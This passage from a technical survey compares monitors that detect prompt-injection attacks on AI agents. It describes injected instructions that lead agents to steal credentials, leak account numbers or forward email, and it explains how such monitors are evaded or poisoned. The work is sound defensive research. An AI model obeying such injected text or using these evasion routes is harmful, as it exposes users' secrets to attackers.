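Tether's perfect score is on the 344 attacks in which it can trace and model every action, so the comparison favours it. The researchers estimate that 28.2 per cent of the recordings in one collection and 22.1 per cent in the other require judging the content, for example whether a permitted edit to a program is malicious, which no rule about data flow can do. For many other recordings, which involve background processes or databases, Tether can only block such activity altogether.

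They also set the permitted files and sites separately for each task, based on its description. They refined the policy by running drafts on recordings from the benchmarks, with a language model proposing changes, until the policy stopped blocking too much harmless work. Its false alarm rate therefore partly reflects this tuning, and a new operator should expect a higher rate at first.

Of the 74 harmless recordings that Tether blocked, 50 involved unrequested edits to protected files, and 7 involved sites not mentioned in the task. A person might want to know about those 57 cases. The other 17 included searches through every file on the computer. Such a search opens the secret files too, so Tether treated them as read and blocked what the agent did next.

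These percentages count blocked recordings, which is only an indirect measure of lost work. After a block, a live agent might finish the task another way or give up. Tether is also a prototype. Its tracing slowed the experiments considerably, and the only encrypted web traffic it can read is traffic to the simulated sites in the tests.

### Withdrawing a tool after an untrusted read

Instead of tracking data, a monitor can withdraw dangerous tools before an injected instruction can trigger them. In Dongol's example, Alice asks her agent to summarise an email. The agent looks up her account number, reads the email, and shows her a summary. The email contains a hidden instruction to fetch a web address that includes the account number. If the monitor withdraws the web-fetching tool when the agent opens the email, the fetch fails, but Alice still gets her summary because summarising doesn't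 require that tool.

To say what this guarantees, Dongol compares the agent with an imaginary reference agent that has the same plan and the same monitor but never obeys untrusted text. Take two runs, $tr_1$ and $tr_2$, that differ in the user's secrets. They leak the difference if the attacker does the same thing in both and observes different results:

$$\mathrm{Act}(tr_1) = \mathrm{Act}(tr_2), \qquad \mathrm{Obs}(tr_1) \neq \mathrm{Obs}(tr_2)$$

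Act stands for the attacker's inputs and Obs for what the attacker observes. The agent is relatively secure if the reference agent could also leak every difference that the agent leaks. An assistant that sends Alice's calendar to anyone who requests a meeting can pass this test, because it would reveal the calendar even without an injection. It fails if an injection can make it send a password reset code as well.

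Dongol proves that an agent is relatively secure if the monitor withdraws every tool an injection could call, at the first untrusted read, and never gives it back. He checked the proof with the theorem-proving software Isabelle. The theorem holds for every plan and doesn't depend on how persuasive the injected text is, but it has conditions:

- A trusted planner must fix the plan before the agent reads anything untrusted.
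- Every call and every untrusted read must go through the monitor.
- Each obeyed instruction may produce only a single call.
- The model must not decide when to obey by looking at a secret or at the monitor's responses.
- The attacker sees the contents and order of the agent's messages but not their timing.

The first condition excludes the build agent because its model chooses each call as it goes along. The theorem doesn't cover most agents that work this way, although removing a tool would still stop them from using it.

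If the monitor withdraws the tool only some time after the email arrives, an injection could first send whatever is already in the agent's memory, even if the agent hasn't yet opened a secret file. In Trace B, the untrusted note arrives with the first message, so the monitor would have to withdraw `http_post` before the agent does anything. That would prevent the theft, but also the summary that the developer asked for. The operator could still allow the summary by splitting the tool in two and withdrawing only the one that can reach outside addresses.

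This loss of function doesn't count against an agent in Dongol's comparison, since the reference agent loses the same tools. As he points out, a monitor that denies every call would be perfectly secure, so operators have to check separately whether the agent can still finish its tasks. For agents that read email and must also reply, he examines two ways to keep the tool for sending email. The agent can start a fresh session, which clears the untrusted text from the model's context, before it gets the tool back. Or the user can approve each message. The approval has to cover the exact recipient and text, because if the user approves only "the next email", an injected call can go first and use up the approval.

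### Availability

Information-flow control is available to developers but still experimental. Microsoft's Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, has included FIDES since version 1.3.0, but developers have to switch it on. Microsoft also worked with GitHub on GitHub Copilot CLI, a command-line coding agent. An experimental setting makes the agent enforce policies for selected tools from GitHub's own Model Context Protocol server, but the setting doesn't yet support servers from other makers. GitHub's server can label files and issues from public repositories as untrusted and those from private repositories as private, if the operator requests it.

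Developers can now also use temporal rules, which take an agent's earlier actions into account. Sistla and colleagues describe Dogwood, which Amazon Web Services introduced in August 2026 to add temporal rules over tool calls to Cedar, an existing policy language. In October the company released Strands Box, which applies such rules to the commands an agent runs in a closed environment. Sistla and colleagues object that these tools don't label files, so they can follow data through only a limited number of steps and miss flows that the agent's software doesn't log.

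For other tool servers, Microsoft has published an open-source gateway that adds the labels. The operator has to describe the format of each tool's results, write a function that labels them, and choose or write a policy. A company with the 12 sources and 5 sinks from the earlier example would do this 17 times. The labels then cover all 60 source-sink pairs without a separate rule for each.

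## Learning what normal tool use looks like

The source-to-sink rule requires someone to decide in advance which files are secret and which addresses are outside. An operator can instead record ordinary sessions, count what the agent usually does, and flag sessions that differ. This approach, called anomaly detection, can catch a theft that nobody wrote a rule for, but it also flags new but harmless work. It descends from work in the 1990s by Stephanie Forrest and colleagues, who recorded the short sequences of system calls (requests to the operating system) that a program made in normal use and treated unfamiliar sequences as a possible sign of an intrusion.

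### Measuring surprise

The numbers in this example are illustrative. Suppose the team has recorded 2,000 transitions in which the build agent read a file and then made another call. In 1,200 of them the next call was a post, and in 800 it was another read. A detector can score each transition by its surprise, in bits:

$$s = -\log_2 P(\text{next call} \mid \text{current call})$$

One bit is the surprise of a fair coin landing heads, and each further bit halves the probability. A post after a read has a probability of 0.6 and scores 0.74 bits. Another read has a probability of 0.4 and scores 1.32 bits. Trace B has a read, another read and then a post, so its scores are unremarkable.

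The detector does better if it counts labelled calls instead of tool names. Say that 50 of the 2,000 transitions began with a read of the credentials:

| Next call after reading the credentials | Times seen | Surprise (bits) |
|---|---|---|
| Read an internal file | 28 | 0.9 |
| Read a secret file | 6 | 3.0 |
| Post to the tracker | 4 | 3.5 |
| Post to a known outside host | 12 | 2.1 |
| Post to a new outside host | 0 | 5.8 |

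Taken literally, a count of zero means a probability of zero and infinite surprise, as if nothing new could ever happen. Add-one smoothing avoids this by adding one to each of the five counts:

$$P = \frac{0 + 1}{50 + 5} = \frac{1}{55}, \qquad s = \log_2 55 \approx 5.8 \text{ bits}$$

The theft in Trace B now stands out, at 5.8 bits. The check of the package service key, which set off a false alarm under the fixed rule, scores only 2.1 bits if the agent has used that service before. The first check with a new service would also score 5.8 bits.

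The score also depends on how much the detector has observed. Zero cases out of 500 would give 1/505, or 9.0 bits, for the same kind of call. A single threshold for all calls can therefore be too strict for some and too loose for others. *Know the Normal, Track the Attack* (Zheng, He and colleagues, 2026) describes a similar problem in a current detector for operating system logs. Common events such as file reads consistently scored low, but rarer ones such as starting a program could score high even when normal. The paper's detector therefore compares each kind of event with its own normal range.

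Transitions link only neighbouring calls, so if the agent made a harmless call between reading the credentials and posting them, the suspicious transition would not appear in the counts. The operator can instead count pairs of calls joined by a data-flow edge, but then the detector misses any data flow that has no recorded edge.

The detector still has to combine these scores into one for the session. Adding them up makes long sessions look suspicious. *Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* (Naagarajan and Streif, 2026) instead scores each session by its most unusual step. The paper's detector looks for agents that fail without reporting an error, but the way it sets its threshold would also work for attacks. The threshold is the score that only a chosen share of trusted sessions exceed, 10 per cent in the main results. An operator can therefore choose the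 false alarm rate before seeing an attack, though the real rate will match it only as long as new sessions resemble the recorded ones.

### TraceAegis: recovering a workflow

Counting transitions ignores the overall plan of a task. TraceAegis, a system by Liu and colleagues, tries to recover that plan from normal traces. One of their test agents helps patients at a clinic. It looks up the symptom keywords that the clinic accepts, asks which departments fit the patient's symptoms, and fetches a checklist from each one. For a patient with ankle pain and psychological distress, it might contact orthopaedics and psychiatry in either order.

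TraceAegis gives each tool a level, starting from the earliest position at which the tool appears in any normal trace. It then adjusts the levels until every normal trace runs from the top level down. The keyword tool ends up on level 1 and the recommendation tool on level 2. All the departments share level 3, because their order can vary. TraceAegis then splits each trace into execution units with one tool per level:

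```
Trace    keywords -> recommendation -> orthopaedics -> psychiatry
Unit 1   keywords -> recommendation -> orthopaedics
Unit 2   keywords -> recommendation -> psychiatry
```

This way, the system can recognise a visit to two familiar departments even if no earlier patient needed that combination.

Next, a language model reads the arguments and results in each unit and writes down the conditions that led to the outcome. For example, it might note that knee pain led to orthopaedics in one unit and arm pain did in another. It then merges these into a rule that accepts either symptom.

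TraceAegis splits a new trace in the same way and checks its structure first. It raises an alert if any unit has a sequence of tools that never occurred in the normal traces. Otherwise, the language model checks the meaning by comparing the conditions in the new trace with those in the rule. For the build agent, a read followed by a post is a familiar unit, so Trace B would probably pass the structural check. The check on meaning would then have to catch the theft, based on the fact that in normal sessions the agent posts to the tracker after reading a log.

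The instructions for that check are to accept two sets of conditions if at least one pair of items is similar, and to ignore extra items. This suits descriptions of symptoms, which vary a lot. An operator checking a list of email recipients would want a stricter comparison.

Liu and colleagues tested TraceAegis on their clinic and purchasing sets, each with 1,300 normal and 300 abnormal traces. Half of the abnormal traces have unfamiliar sequences of calls. The other half have familiar sequences with the wrong content, such as a referral to psychiatry for back pain. The table gives F1 scores for TraceAegis and for the same language model judging the traces without it:

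| Language model | Clinic: model alone | Clinic: TraceAegis | Purchasing: model alone | Purchasing: TraceAegis |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma-3-27B | 0.666 | 0.814 | 0.512 | 0.739 |
| GPT-OSS-120B | 0.865 | 0.948 | 0.648 | 0.936 |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 0.670 | 0.897 | 0.543 | 0.922 |
| Qwen3-235B | 0.843 | 0.942 | 0.846 | 0.906 |
| DeepSeek-V3 | 0.850 | 0.965 | 0.842 | 0.932 |

TraceAegis improved every model, though the choice of model still matters a lot. In purchasing, it caught all 150 unfamiliar sequences with each of the five models, but of the 150 traces with the wrong content, it caught 130 with the best models and only 64 with Gemma.

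Liu and colleagues don't report how often TraceAegis flagged harmless traces, but their precision, recall and accuracy figures are consistent with a test that included about 300 of them. If that number is right, TraceAegis flagged about 3 per cent of harmless clinic traces with DeepSeek-V3, 8 per cent with GPT-OSS-120B and 36 per cent with Gemma. Even a 3 per cent rate could be a burden for an operator with thousands of sessions a day and few attacks.

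The levels mattered more than the conditions. Removing the levels lowered the F1 score with GPT-OSS-120B in the clinic from 0.948 to 0.499, well below the 0.865 that the model achieved without TraceAegis. Using whole traces instead of units, the system had merged visits to gynaecology, gastroenterology and oncology into one rule that left out a step. Removing the conditions and keeping the levels lowered the score only to 0.892.

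TraceAegis also did well in a red-team exercise, in which a technology company's own staff attacked one of its agents. The agent looks for software vulnerabilities in five stages. In one attack, a hidden instruction in a public configuration file made the agent write its report before the runtime check that the report depends on. TraceAegis detected 132 of 140 such sequence anomalies, or 94.3 per cent. The paper doesn't report how many harmless sessions TraceAegis flagged during the exercise.

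All three agents follow a fairly fixed workflow. A general coding assistant may edit a file, search the web and run tests in almost any order, so its normal traces would contain fewer stable units to learn from.

### Agent-Sentry: paths from normal use and attacks

TraceAegis learns only from normal traces, while the March 2026 version of Agent-Sentry also learns from recorded attacks. For every call that has an effect outside the agent, such as a payment, Agent-Sentry records which lookups and actions came before it and whether each argument came from the user's message or an earlier result. This version finds each argument's origin by matching text, with special handling for account numbers and email addresses, rather than asking the agent to declare it. It doesn't keep the arguments' values, so two users who pay different invoices in the same way produce the same recorded path.

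Sequeira and colleagues sort these paths into three graphs, one for paths that occurred only in harmless sessions, one for paths that occurred only in attacks, and one for paths that occurred in both. When the agent proposes a call, Agent-Sentry allows the call if its path is in the harmless graph and blocks it if the path is in the attack graph.

If the path is ambiguous or new, a second language model judges whether the call fits the user's request. Agent-Sentry gives this model the request, the steps so far and the proposed call, but withholds the content the agent has retrieved because it may contain injected text. Withholding it doesn't help in Trace B, where the hidden paragraph is part of the request.

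Sequeira and colleagues tested the system on 1,455 harmless and 5,278 attack traces from banking, Slack, travel and office tasks. They varied the share of traces from which it learned, but always tested it on all of them:

| Traces used for learning (per cent) | Harmless traces allowed (per cent) | Attacks not blocked (per cent) |
|---|---|---|
| 50 | 79.6 | 7.5 |
| 90 | 92.1 | 8.9 |
| 100 | 94.6 | 9.5 |

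The bottom row is a test on the training data. The other rows mix training traces with new ones, and an operator cares about the new ones. If Agent-Sentry allowed 94.6 per cent of the harmless training traces, the top two rows imply that it allowed only about 65 to 70 per cent of the harmless new ones and blocked roughly one in three.

More training data also let more attacks through, because some attacks follow the same path as a harmless task. If the training data contains only the attack, the system blocks the path outright. Once the data also includes the harmless task, the path becomes ambiguous, and the second model sometimes makes the wrong decision.

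When the graphs included all the traces, 62 per cent of banking traces and 70 per cent of Slack traces followed paths that occur in both harmless sessions and attacks, compared with 27 per cent for travel tasks and 23 per cent for office tasks. The order of the calls and the rough origin of the arguments were therefore enough to tell attacks from harmless sessions in most travel and office traces, but in fewer than half of the banking and Slack traces.

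The learned graphs still helped the full system block more attacks and allow more harmless traces. The second model alone let 19.0 per cent of attacks through and allowed 91.0 per cent of harmless traces.

Sequeira and colleagues also compared Agent-Sentry with other defences on AgentDojo. Agent-Sentry cut the attack success rate from 47.7 to 3.7 per cent, while the share of tasks completed fell only from 77.3 to 76.3 per cent. The average time per task rose from about 4 to 8 seconds. CaMeL, which plans the calls before the agent reads untrusted text, stopped every attack but completed only 37.1 per cent of the tasks and took 27 seconds per task. But the researchers built their own collection of traces by extending AgentDojo. If the learned graphs came from that collection, Agent-Sentry had an advantage over defences that don't learn from examples.

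### How much the graph adds

Agent-Sentry uses the graph and the second model together, so it is hard to tell how much information the graph itself contains. Zavrak separated the two kinds of evidence by giving detectors different parts of the same sessions. The sessions came from RAS-Eval, which covers 80 tasks and has 605 harmless sessions and 3,797 attacked ones. The detectors learned from labelled examples of both harmless and attacked sessions, unlike a pure anomaly detector.

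Metadata here means the tool's name, the length of its response and a number computed from the arguments that doesn't preserve their meaning. Content means the text of the arguments and responses, which a small language model converts into lists of numbers that represent its meaning. A graph network combines each call's numbers with those of the calls linked to it. For comparison, Zavrak also tried XGBoost, which builds many small decision trees that each correct errors of the earlier ones, and a neural network that doesn't use the graph.

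| Detector | Input | AUROC |
|---|---|---|
| Graph network | Metadata | 0.640 |
| Graph network | Content | 0.917 |
| Neural network without the graph | Content | 0.896 |
| XGBoost | Content, pooled | 0.975 |

"Pooled" means that XGBoost, the most accurate detector, received only the average and maximum of the numbers across all calls in a session. It therefore had no information about the order of the calls or which data went where. The table shows only the best of three graph networks. Another scored 0.891, slightly below the network without a graph.

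These results don't support the claim that attacks can be detected from the shape of a tool-call graph, but they don't refute it either, because RAS-Eval contains few attacks that would change the shape. In 81.9 per cent of its attacks, the attacker altered both the inputs and the outputs of tools, for example by replacing a file path and falsifying a response. In another 11.1 per cent, the attacker altered only outputs. Such changes leave traces in the text but may not change the order of the calls. By contrast, the theft in Trace B adds two calls and an edge from a secret to an outside address, so RAS-Eval doesn't directly test read-and-send chains. Zavrak's edges also have no direction and often miss real data flows. The overlapping paths in Agent-Sentry's banking and Slack traces are better evidence about shape, because AgentDojo's injections do trigger extra calls. These overlaps suggest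 that shape alone often isn't enough to detect an attack.

The remaining 7.2 per cent of attacks altered only the inputs. The graph network with content caught 21 of these 57 sessions (36.8 per cent), compared with 86.9 per cent of the attacks that altered both inputs and outputs. An input-only attack resembles the redirected post in the build example, which changes very little of the text. Because the 36.8 per cent figure comes from a single run with few such sessions, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 25 to 50 per cent.

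The best detectors, XGBoost and a random forest (another method based on decision trees), had nearly the same AUROC, 0.975 and 0.974. But at the standard threshold, XGBoost flagged 7.1 per cent of harmless sessions and the random forest flagged 19.1 per cent. On ATBench, a second collection with shorter sessions and subtler attacks, no detector exceeded an AUROC of 0.784.

Zavrak also tested whether a detector learns faster from a few labelled attacks if it is first trained only on harmless sessions. With labels for 10 per cent of the RAS-Eval sessions, the pretrained network did worse, reaching an AUROC of 0.686, compared with 0.800 for the same network without pretraining. This result covers only one training method, but operators shouldn't assume that a large archive of harmless sessions can make up for a lack of recorded attacks.

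### Shortcuts in the tests

A detector can score well on test data without learning what an attack looks like, for example by memorising tasks. Researchers usually divide recorded sessions at random into a training set and a test set. RAS-Eval has thousands of sessions but only 80 tasks, so a random split puts most tasks in both sets. The detector can then learn which tools go with each task and how often sessions of that task were attacks.

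Zavrak measured this by keeping all sessions of a task on the same side of the split. With metadata, one graph network's AUROC fell from 0.898 to 0.640, so the random split had inflated it by 0.258. With content, it fell from 0.992 to 0.891. An operator who tests a detector on past sessions should hold out whole tasks, because users will keep giving the agent new ones.

Keeping tasks apart doesn't remove every shortcut for a detector. All the RAS-Eval attacks targeted one language model, GLM-4-Flash, while the harmless sessions came from eight, so a detector that reads the text could partly be recognising GLM-4-Flash's style. Zavrak found that metadata did not identify the model but acknowledges that the text might. There were too few harmless GLM-4-Flash sessions to test the detector on that model alone.

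*DriftNet* (Pinjari and Saint-Germain, 2026) describes a detector trained to find the step at which an injection enters a session and each later step that serves the attacker. Its inputs include the text and whether a call's recipient is among the user's contacts, because forwarding the same document can be routine work or theft depending on who gets it. On tasks that were not in the training data, the detector reached an F1 score of 0.983. It also caught 93.2 per cent of attacks in which the agent obeys only after further harmless steps, compared with 17.1 per cent for a simpler detector.

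The results are impressive for a small model that reads only logs, but the sessions are synthetic and all come from one generator. Looking up a session's fictional world (its user, organisation and contacts) is enough to classify 86 per cent of sessions correctly. Pinjari and Saint-Germain designed the contact information so that it can't reveal which world a session belongs to, but they acknowledge that the text still might.

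A detector can also use session length as a shortcut. In the study by Naagarajan and Streif, step count alone detected failed sessions with an AUROC of 0.716. Injected calls lengthen a session, as in Trace B, which is twice as long as Trace A. In the TraceAegis test data, normal clinic traces have 4.67 calls on average, unfamiliar abnormal ones 3.41 and familiar abnormal ones 6.63. Liu and colleagues compared their system with language models but not with a length-based rule, which would be easy to test, so it's unclear how much of the task such a rule could solve.

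### When normal behaviour changes

Even a detector that passed all these tests can become outdated through drift, which is a change in the agent's normal behavior. If the build team gives its agent a new upload tool, every session that uses the tool is unfamiliar to the detector. The same happens when the team starts to use the agent for a new task, or when a new version of the language model solves old tasks in a different way. Drift can therefore cause the detector to block many harmless sessions. The estimate from Agent-Sentry's results is that about a third of unfamiliar harmless sessions get blocked.

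Changes in writing style can also make a detector less accurate. Naagarajan and Streif used a language model to play the customer in their test conversations. When they switched to a different model, the AUROC of a detector based on the conversation's text fell from 0.805 to 0.547, close to chance. A detector that used the agent's internal activations stayed at about 0.8. Operators without access to the activations would have to retest a text-based detector whenever the people or models writing to the agent change.

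A rolling baseline, which always covers the most recent sessions, adapts automatically to drift, but also to gradual misuse. *From Admission to Invariants* (2026) demonstrates this in a simulation of an agent whose choice of tools slowly shifts. The detector's anomaly score rose to 0.388 at step 261, then fell to 0.270 by step 299, because the shifted behaviour had become part of the baseline. A detector based on fixed rules would also have missed the change, because the agent never broke one. In another run, the agent passed work along increasingly long chains of delegation, which the detector could not measure because it counted only how often the agent used each tool.

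*MCPShield* (2026), which monitors tool servers, uses a language model to compare a server's recent behaviour with an earlier period and rate the drift from 1 to 5. Under its instructions, the model can treat new web domains or a different number of tools as harmless. Evidence such as the reading of sensitive files can raise the rating. This should reduce false alarms after ordinary updates, but the model could misjudge a change.

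Sequeira and colleagues propose updating Agent-Sentry's graphs periodically, after software or a developer has classified each new path as harmless or harmful. They haven't built this part. It would let the operator control what enters the baseline, but someone would have to review unfamiliar sessions by hand whenever the software couldn't classify them confidently.

### Attacks in the training data

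A baseline learned from real sessions may already contain successful attacks. Suppose one of the 50 transitions after a credentials read in the illustrative example had been an unnoticed theft. With add-one smoothing, the probability of a post to a new outside host would be 2/55, and its surprise would fall from 5.8 to 4.8 bits. With five thefts among the 50, the surprise would be 3.2 bits, about the same as for reading a second secret file. If the software also treats an address as known once the agent has contacted it, a second theft using the same address wouldn't count as a post to a new host.

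A single attack could have a lasting effect on TraceAegis, because new traces can add relations between tools but never remove them. If an attack introduces a new sequence of calls, later harmless traces won't remove it. The operator has to find and delete the attack's trace, then rebuild the baseline.

Most of these systems assume that their training data can be trusted. Zavrak assumes a supply of harmless sessions, and Zheng, He and colleagues explicitly exclude poisoned training data from the threats they consider. Agent-Sentry relies on correct labels, because an attack labelled as harmless would move its path out of the attack graph. Calls on that path would then go to the second model or, if no recorded attack shares the path, be allowed without review.

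Selecting sessions by their outcome isn't enough to keep attacks out of the baseline. Naagarajan and Streif build theirs from sessions in which the agent completed the task, which makes sense for detecting failures. But the agent in Trace B also completes its task by giving the developer the summary, so its session would enter the baseline despite the theft.

It is safer to train on sessions from a closed test environment, where the team has written or checked everything the agent reads. Those sessions will be less varied than real ones, so there will be more false alarms in the first weeks of use. The operator can also run the source-to-sink rule over recorded sessions before training on them and review whatever it flags. If the team keeps the original baseline alongside the rolling one, it can still detect a slow change that has become part of the rolling baseline.

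## Comparing the calls with what the user asked for

The source-to-sink rule requires a list of secret files, and a learned baseline requires a record of past sessions. An operator can also compare an agent's calls with the user's current request. If a developer asks the agent to check whether the team's package key still works, the agent has to send the key to the package service, even though the source-to-sink rule flags that call. But the agent has no reason to send a key anywhere if the developer asked only for a summary of a build log.

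Yao, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *AgentTracer*, compare each call with the request on three points: the kind of action, its target, and any constraints on how the agent may carry it out. If the request consists only of the sentence the developer typed, the comparison for Trace B looks like this:

| Call | Action | Target | Constraint |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. Read `logs/build.log` | Fits | Fits | None applies |
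| 2. Read `config/credentials` | Fits, because the task involves reading a file | Violated: the request concerns the log | None applies |
| 3. Post to `diagnostics.example` | Fits, because the task involves a post | Violated: the request names the tracker | Violated: the body isn't a summary of the log |
| 4. Post to the tracker | Fits | Fits | Fits |

The user's request requires neither reading the credentials nor posting data outside. But the theft uses the same types of action as the task, so a check based only on the type of action would allow all four calls. Comparing the agent's final answer with the request would usually miss the theft too. In *Silent Egress* (2026), a study of agents that leak data through web requests, the final answer looked harmless in 95 per cent of successful attacks.

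Users usually leave steps out of their requests, such as finding and opening the report they want an agent to send to an auditor. AgentTracer fills in these steps from a knowledge base that covers 11 classes of operation and lists the supporting steps each may need. In one example, the user asks the agent to summarise a payroll file if the total exceeds 1 million dollars, and to send only the summary to a named auditor. AgentTracer adds permission to find and read the file, and treats the recipient, the threshold and the word "only" as constraints. A vaguer request, such as "Find out why the build failed", rules out less. It could justify reading the configuration folder, and perhaps even contacting a diagnostics service.

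### Planning the calls in advance

IPIGuard (An et al., August 2025) determines most of the agent's calls before the agent reads anything untrusted. A planning model receives the user's instruction, the tool descriptions and some background, such as documents the user has declared trustworthy. It writes a graph in which each node is a call and each edge leads to a later call that needs that call's result. Unlike the graphs earlier in this report, which come from a log of what the agent did, this graph sets out which calls the agent may make.

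In one of their examples, a traveller asks for the rating, price and address of a hotel called City Hub, and for a calendar reminder if the first two are acceptable. In shortened form, the plan is:

```
1  get_rating(City Hub)
2  get_price(City Hub)
3  get_address(City Hub)
4  create_event(City Hub, location: unknown)    needs 1, 2, 3
```

The software runs the calls in an order that follows the edges. Before call 4, the model replaces "unknown" with the address that call 3 returned. One of the hotel's reviews contains a hidden instruction to book a room somewhere else, but the plan has no booking call, so the agent can't make one.

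A fixed plan fails when the next step depends on what the agent reads. An and colleagues let the agent add calls during the task, but only calls that retrieve information. For example, a user asks the agent to find the chat channel where Alice asked about a coffee mug and to reply there. The plan includes a call to read one channel, but once the agent has the list of channels, it adds calls to read the others. Their system drops any added call that would change something, such as sending a message or making a payment.

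This exception is reasonable for payments but weaker against data theft, which starts with a read. Suppose the build agent itself fetches the troubleshooting note from the web. The hidden paragraph could still lead it to add a call that reads the credentials. IPIGuard would drop the post to `diagnostics.example`, but if it counts web fetching as a read, the agent could send the credentials out in a web address. An and colleagues consider some of the attacks recorded as successful to have no real-world impact, because they only made the agent visit a website the attacker had chosen. That is true only if the address contains no private data. An operator should therefore treat web fetching as a sink and allow it only where the plan includes it.

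Some tasks require the agent to act on what it reads, such as "read my to-do list and pay the bills on it". IPIGuard handles these conservatively and completes fewer of them. An and colleagues argue that users should avoid such requests, because once a user has told the agent to follow a document, an instruction planted in it looks like part of the task. The advice is sound, but it rules out much of what people want from an assistant. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* calls the question of which of these tasks can be secured the deepest open problem in the field.

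The plan also doesn't help if the attacker wants a call that is already in it. In another example, a user asks the agent to pay Spotify the difference after a 10 per cent price rise. The plan contains a payment with an unknown recipient and amount, and the transaction history contains an instruction to send as much money as possible to another account. Before the model fills in the payment, IPIGuard asks it to write separate calls for any new instructions it has found. IPIGuard doesn't run these calls but tells the model that they succeeded. Because the attacker's request now appears to have been carried out, the model fills in the original payment correctly, as 5 dollars to Spotify.

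An and colleagues tested IPIGuard on AgentDojo, with 97 tasks and 629 attack cases. Averaged over four kinds of attack on GPT-4o-mini, the success rate fell from 13.16 to 0.69 per cent. The next table covers only the most effective kind and shows what each part contributes:

| Version | Harmless tasks completed (per cent) | Attacks that succeeded (per cent) |
|---|---|---|
| No defence | 68.04 | 27.19 |
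| Plan only | 52.58 | 3.18 |
| Plan and extra reads | 64.95 | 4.77 |
| Plan and fake responses | 51.55 | 0.32 |
| All three | 69.07 | 0.64 |

The plan alone stopped most attacks, but the agent needed the extra reads to stay useful. (Elsewhere the paper reports that the agent completed 67.01 per cent of tasks with the full system.) The average task took 14 seconds instead of 7.

IPIGuard did less well in a later test by another team. In *AgentSentry*, Zhang, Xu and colleagues (2026) ran it with three other models on a newer version of AgentDojo with 949 attack cases. Between 5.3 and 8.8 per cent of attacks succeeded on average, and IPIGuard intervened in 37 to 44 per cent of harmless tasks. The share of tasks completed fell by only 3 to 8 percentage points, so an intervention didn't always ruin the task. Zhang and colleagues were comparing IPIGuard with their own system, but the gap between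 the two tests is large enough that an operator should measure both rates before relying on a plan.

### Rerunning a step without the suspicious text

AgentSentry, a different system from Agent-Sentry despite the name, lets the agent choose its calls as it goes along. Whenever a tool returns a result, AgentSentry pauses the agent before its next action and tests whether text in the result has changed its course:

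1. It records the call that the agent proposes.
2. It replaces the user's request with a question about whether the retrieved text is trying to direct the agent. The model quotes any such passages and names the action they call for.
3. It deletes those passages from a copy of the result.
4. It restores the user's request and asks the model for its next call again, using the cleaned copy.

No tool runs during the test. Let $\hat{p}(a)$ be the share of reruns in which the model proposes the same call $a$. The main score is

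$$S = \hat{p}(a \mid \text{request, original result}) - \hat{p}(a \mid \text{request, cleaned result})$$

Zhang and colleagues use one rerun per condition, so each share is 0 or 1. If $S = 1$, the call depended on the deleted passages. AgentSentry also checks that the action named in step 2 disappears when the passages are deleted. If both tests are positive, it raises an alarm, discards the proposed call and lets the agent continue from the cleaned result.

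In one session, a user wants a lunch appointment, and an existing calendar entry contains a hidden instruction to read the user's unread email and forward it to a stranger. The agent looks up a contact and creates the appointment. It would have made both calls without the hidden text, so AgentSentry allows them. Then the agent proposes to read the unread email. It no longer proposes this when AgentSentry removes the instruction, so it never opens the email and has nothing to forward.

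With AgentSentry, none of the 949 attacks succeeded on GPT-4o, GPT-3.5-turbo or Qwen3-Max, whereas an average of 26 to 39 per cent succeeded without a defence. For each model, this result is compatible with a true rate of up to 0.39 per cent on similar attacks. In the office tasks, the agent finished 92.3 per cent of attacked tasks with AgentSentry, which lets it continue after an alarm, but only 55.4 per cent when an alarm ended the session. AgentSentry intervened in 2 to 5 of the 97 harmless tasks and increased the average time for a harmless task from 17 to 38 seconds.

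Longer sessions were harder to protect. In 96 workflows with up to 24 steps between the injection and its effect, 11 attacks succeeded. Half of these workflows tested a theft in which the agent collects more data than the user asked for but sends its message to the right person. The equivalent in the build example would be a tracker post that includes the credentials. Each call in such a session may look normal, so AgentSentry also checks for a trend over three consecutive tool results. This check reduced the number of successful thefts from 43 to 7 out of 48.

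Zhang and colleagues also designed attacks against AgentSentry's own mechanisms. Of the 19 that worked on an undefended agent, two also worked against AgentSentry. Both planted a wrong recipient that looked like ordinary data, so AgentSentry had no instruction to delete. According to *Prompt Injection Through Forensic Evidence* (2026), most current defences miss false facts like these because they look for commands. But false claims don't always work. In a test the same paper cites, comments claiming that the code had already been audited had no significant effect on eight code-reviewing models.

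### Recovering the chain after an alert

An alert may concern only the last call in a chain. In an example from Yao and colleagues, a user asks an agent to download a software release and upload it to GitHub. Hidden text on the download page leads the agent to add the attacker's access key to the account, read received emails, verify the account, and clear its own working memory. If only the memory clearing triggered an alert, an investigator who examined just that call would leave the attacker's key in place.

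Data-flow edges may not connect these calls, because the call that clears the memory takes no arguments and so can't contain data from an earlier result. AgentTracer instead uses the agent's written reasoning, where the agent may mention that the instruction to clear the memory came from the download page. In AgentTracer's graph, the nodes are the user's request and the items the agent retrieved or changed. Each edge is a call, and it starts at the node the agent gave as its reason for making that call.

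AgentTracer starts from the suspicious call and finds the user request that came before it. It builds the graph for that part of the log and marks every call that violates the request in its action, target or constraints. It then follows the marked edges backwards from the suspicious call until there are no more. If the path ends at something retrieved from outside, AgentTracer reports that item as the source of the injection and the calls on the path as the attack. If the path ends elsewhere, AgentTracer doesn't classify the event as an injection, because the agent may have made a mistake.

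Yao and colleagues tested AgentTracer on 600 logs of successful attacks, half from each of two benchmarks. They mixed the attacks into five months of ordinary logs with 1,800 user requests and 9,000 tool calls. AgentTracer identified 97 per cent of the attacks as injections. In 94 per cent of the attacks, it found the exact log line where the hostile text entered. It recovered 90 per cent of the malicious calls, and 94 per cent of the calls it reported were malicious.

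They then compared it with other tools on 100 attacks:

| Tool | Entry point found (per cent) | Malicious calls recovered (per cent) | Reported calls that were malicious (per cent) |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentTracer | 94 | 88.1 | 93.2 |
| AgentArmor | 76 | 94.1 | 53.6 |
| Codex, asked to read the logs | 70 | 46.2 | 51.0 |
| NeuroTaint | 40 | 48.0 | 91.4 |

The researchers had to rebuild some of the competing tools from their published descriptions, which may have put those tools at a disadvantage. Every test also began with a known suspicious call, so the 97 per cent measures how well AgentTracer explains an alert, not how well it finds attacks without one.

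A smaller test suggests how well the comparison would work as an alarm. In 100 harmless sessions, AgentTracer marked 38 of 394 graph edges as violating the request. Yao and colleagues count 13 of these as errors, a false-positive rate of 3.52 per cent, because the agent had strayed from its task in the other 25. An operator looking for attacks would still have to review all 38. If each fell in a different session, 38 of the 100 sessions would raise an alert. AgentTracer avoids most of these false alarms by starting from an alert and requiring a path back to outside content.

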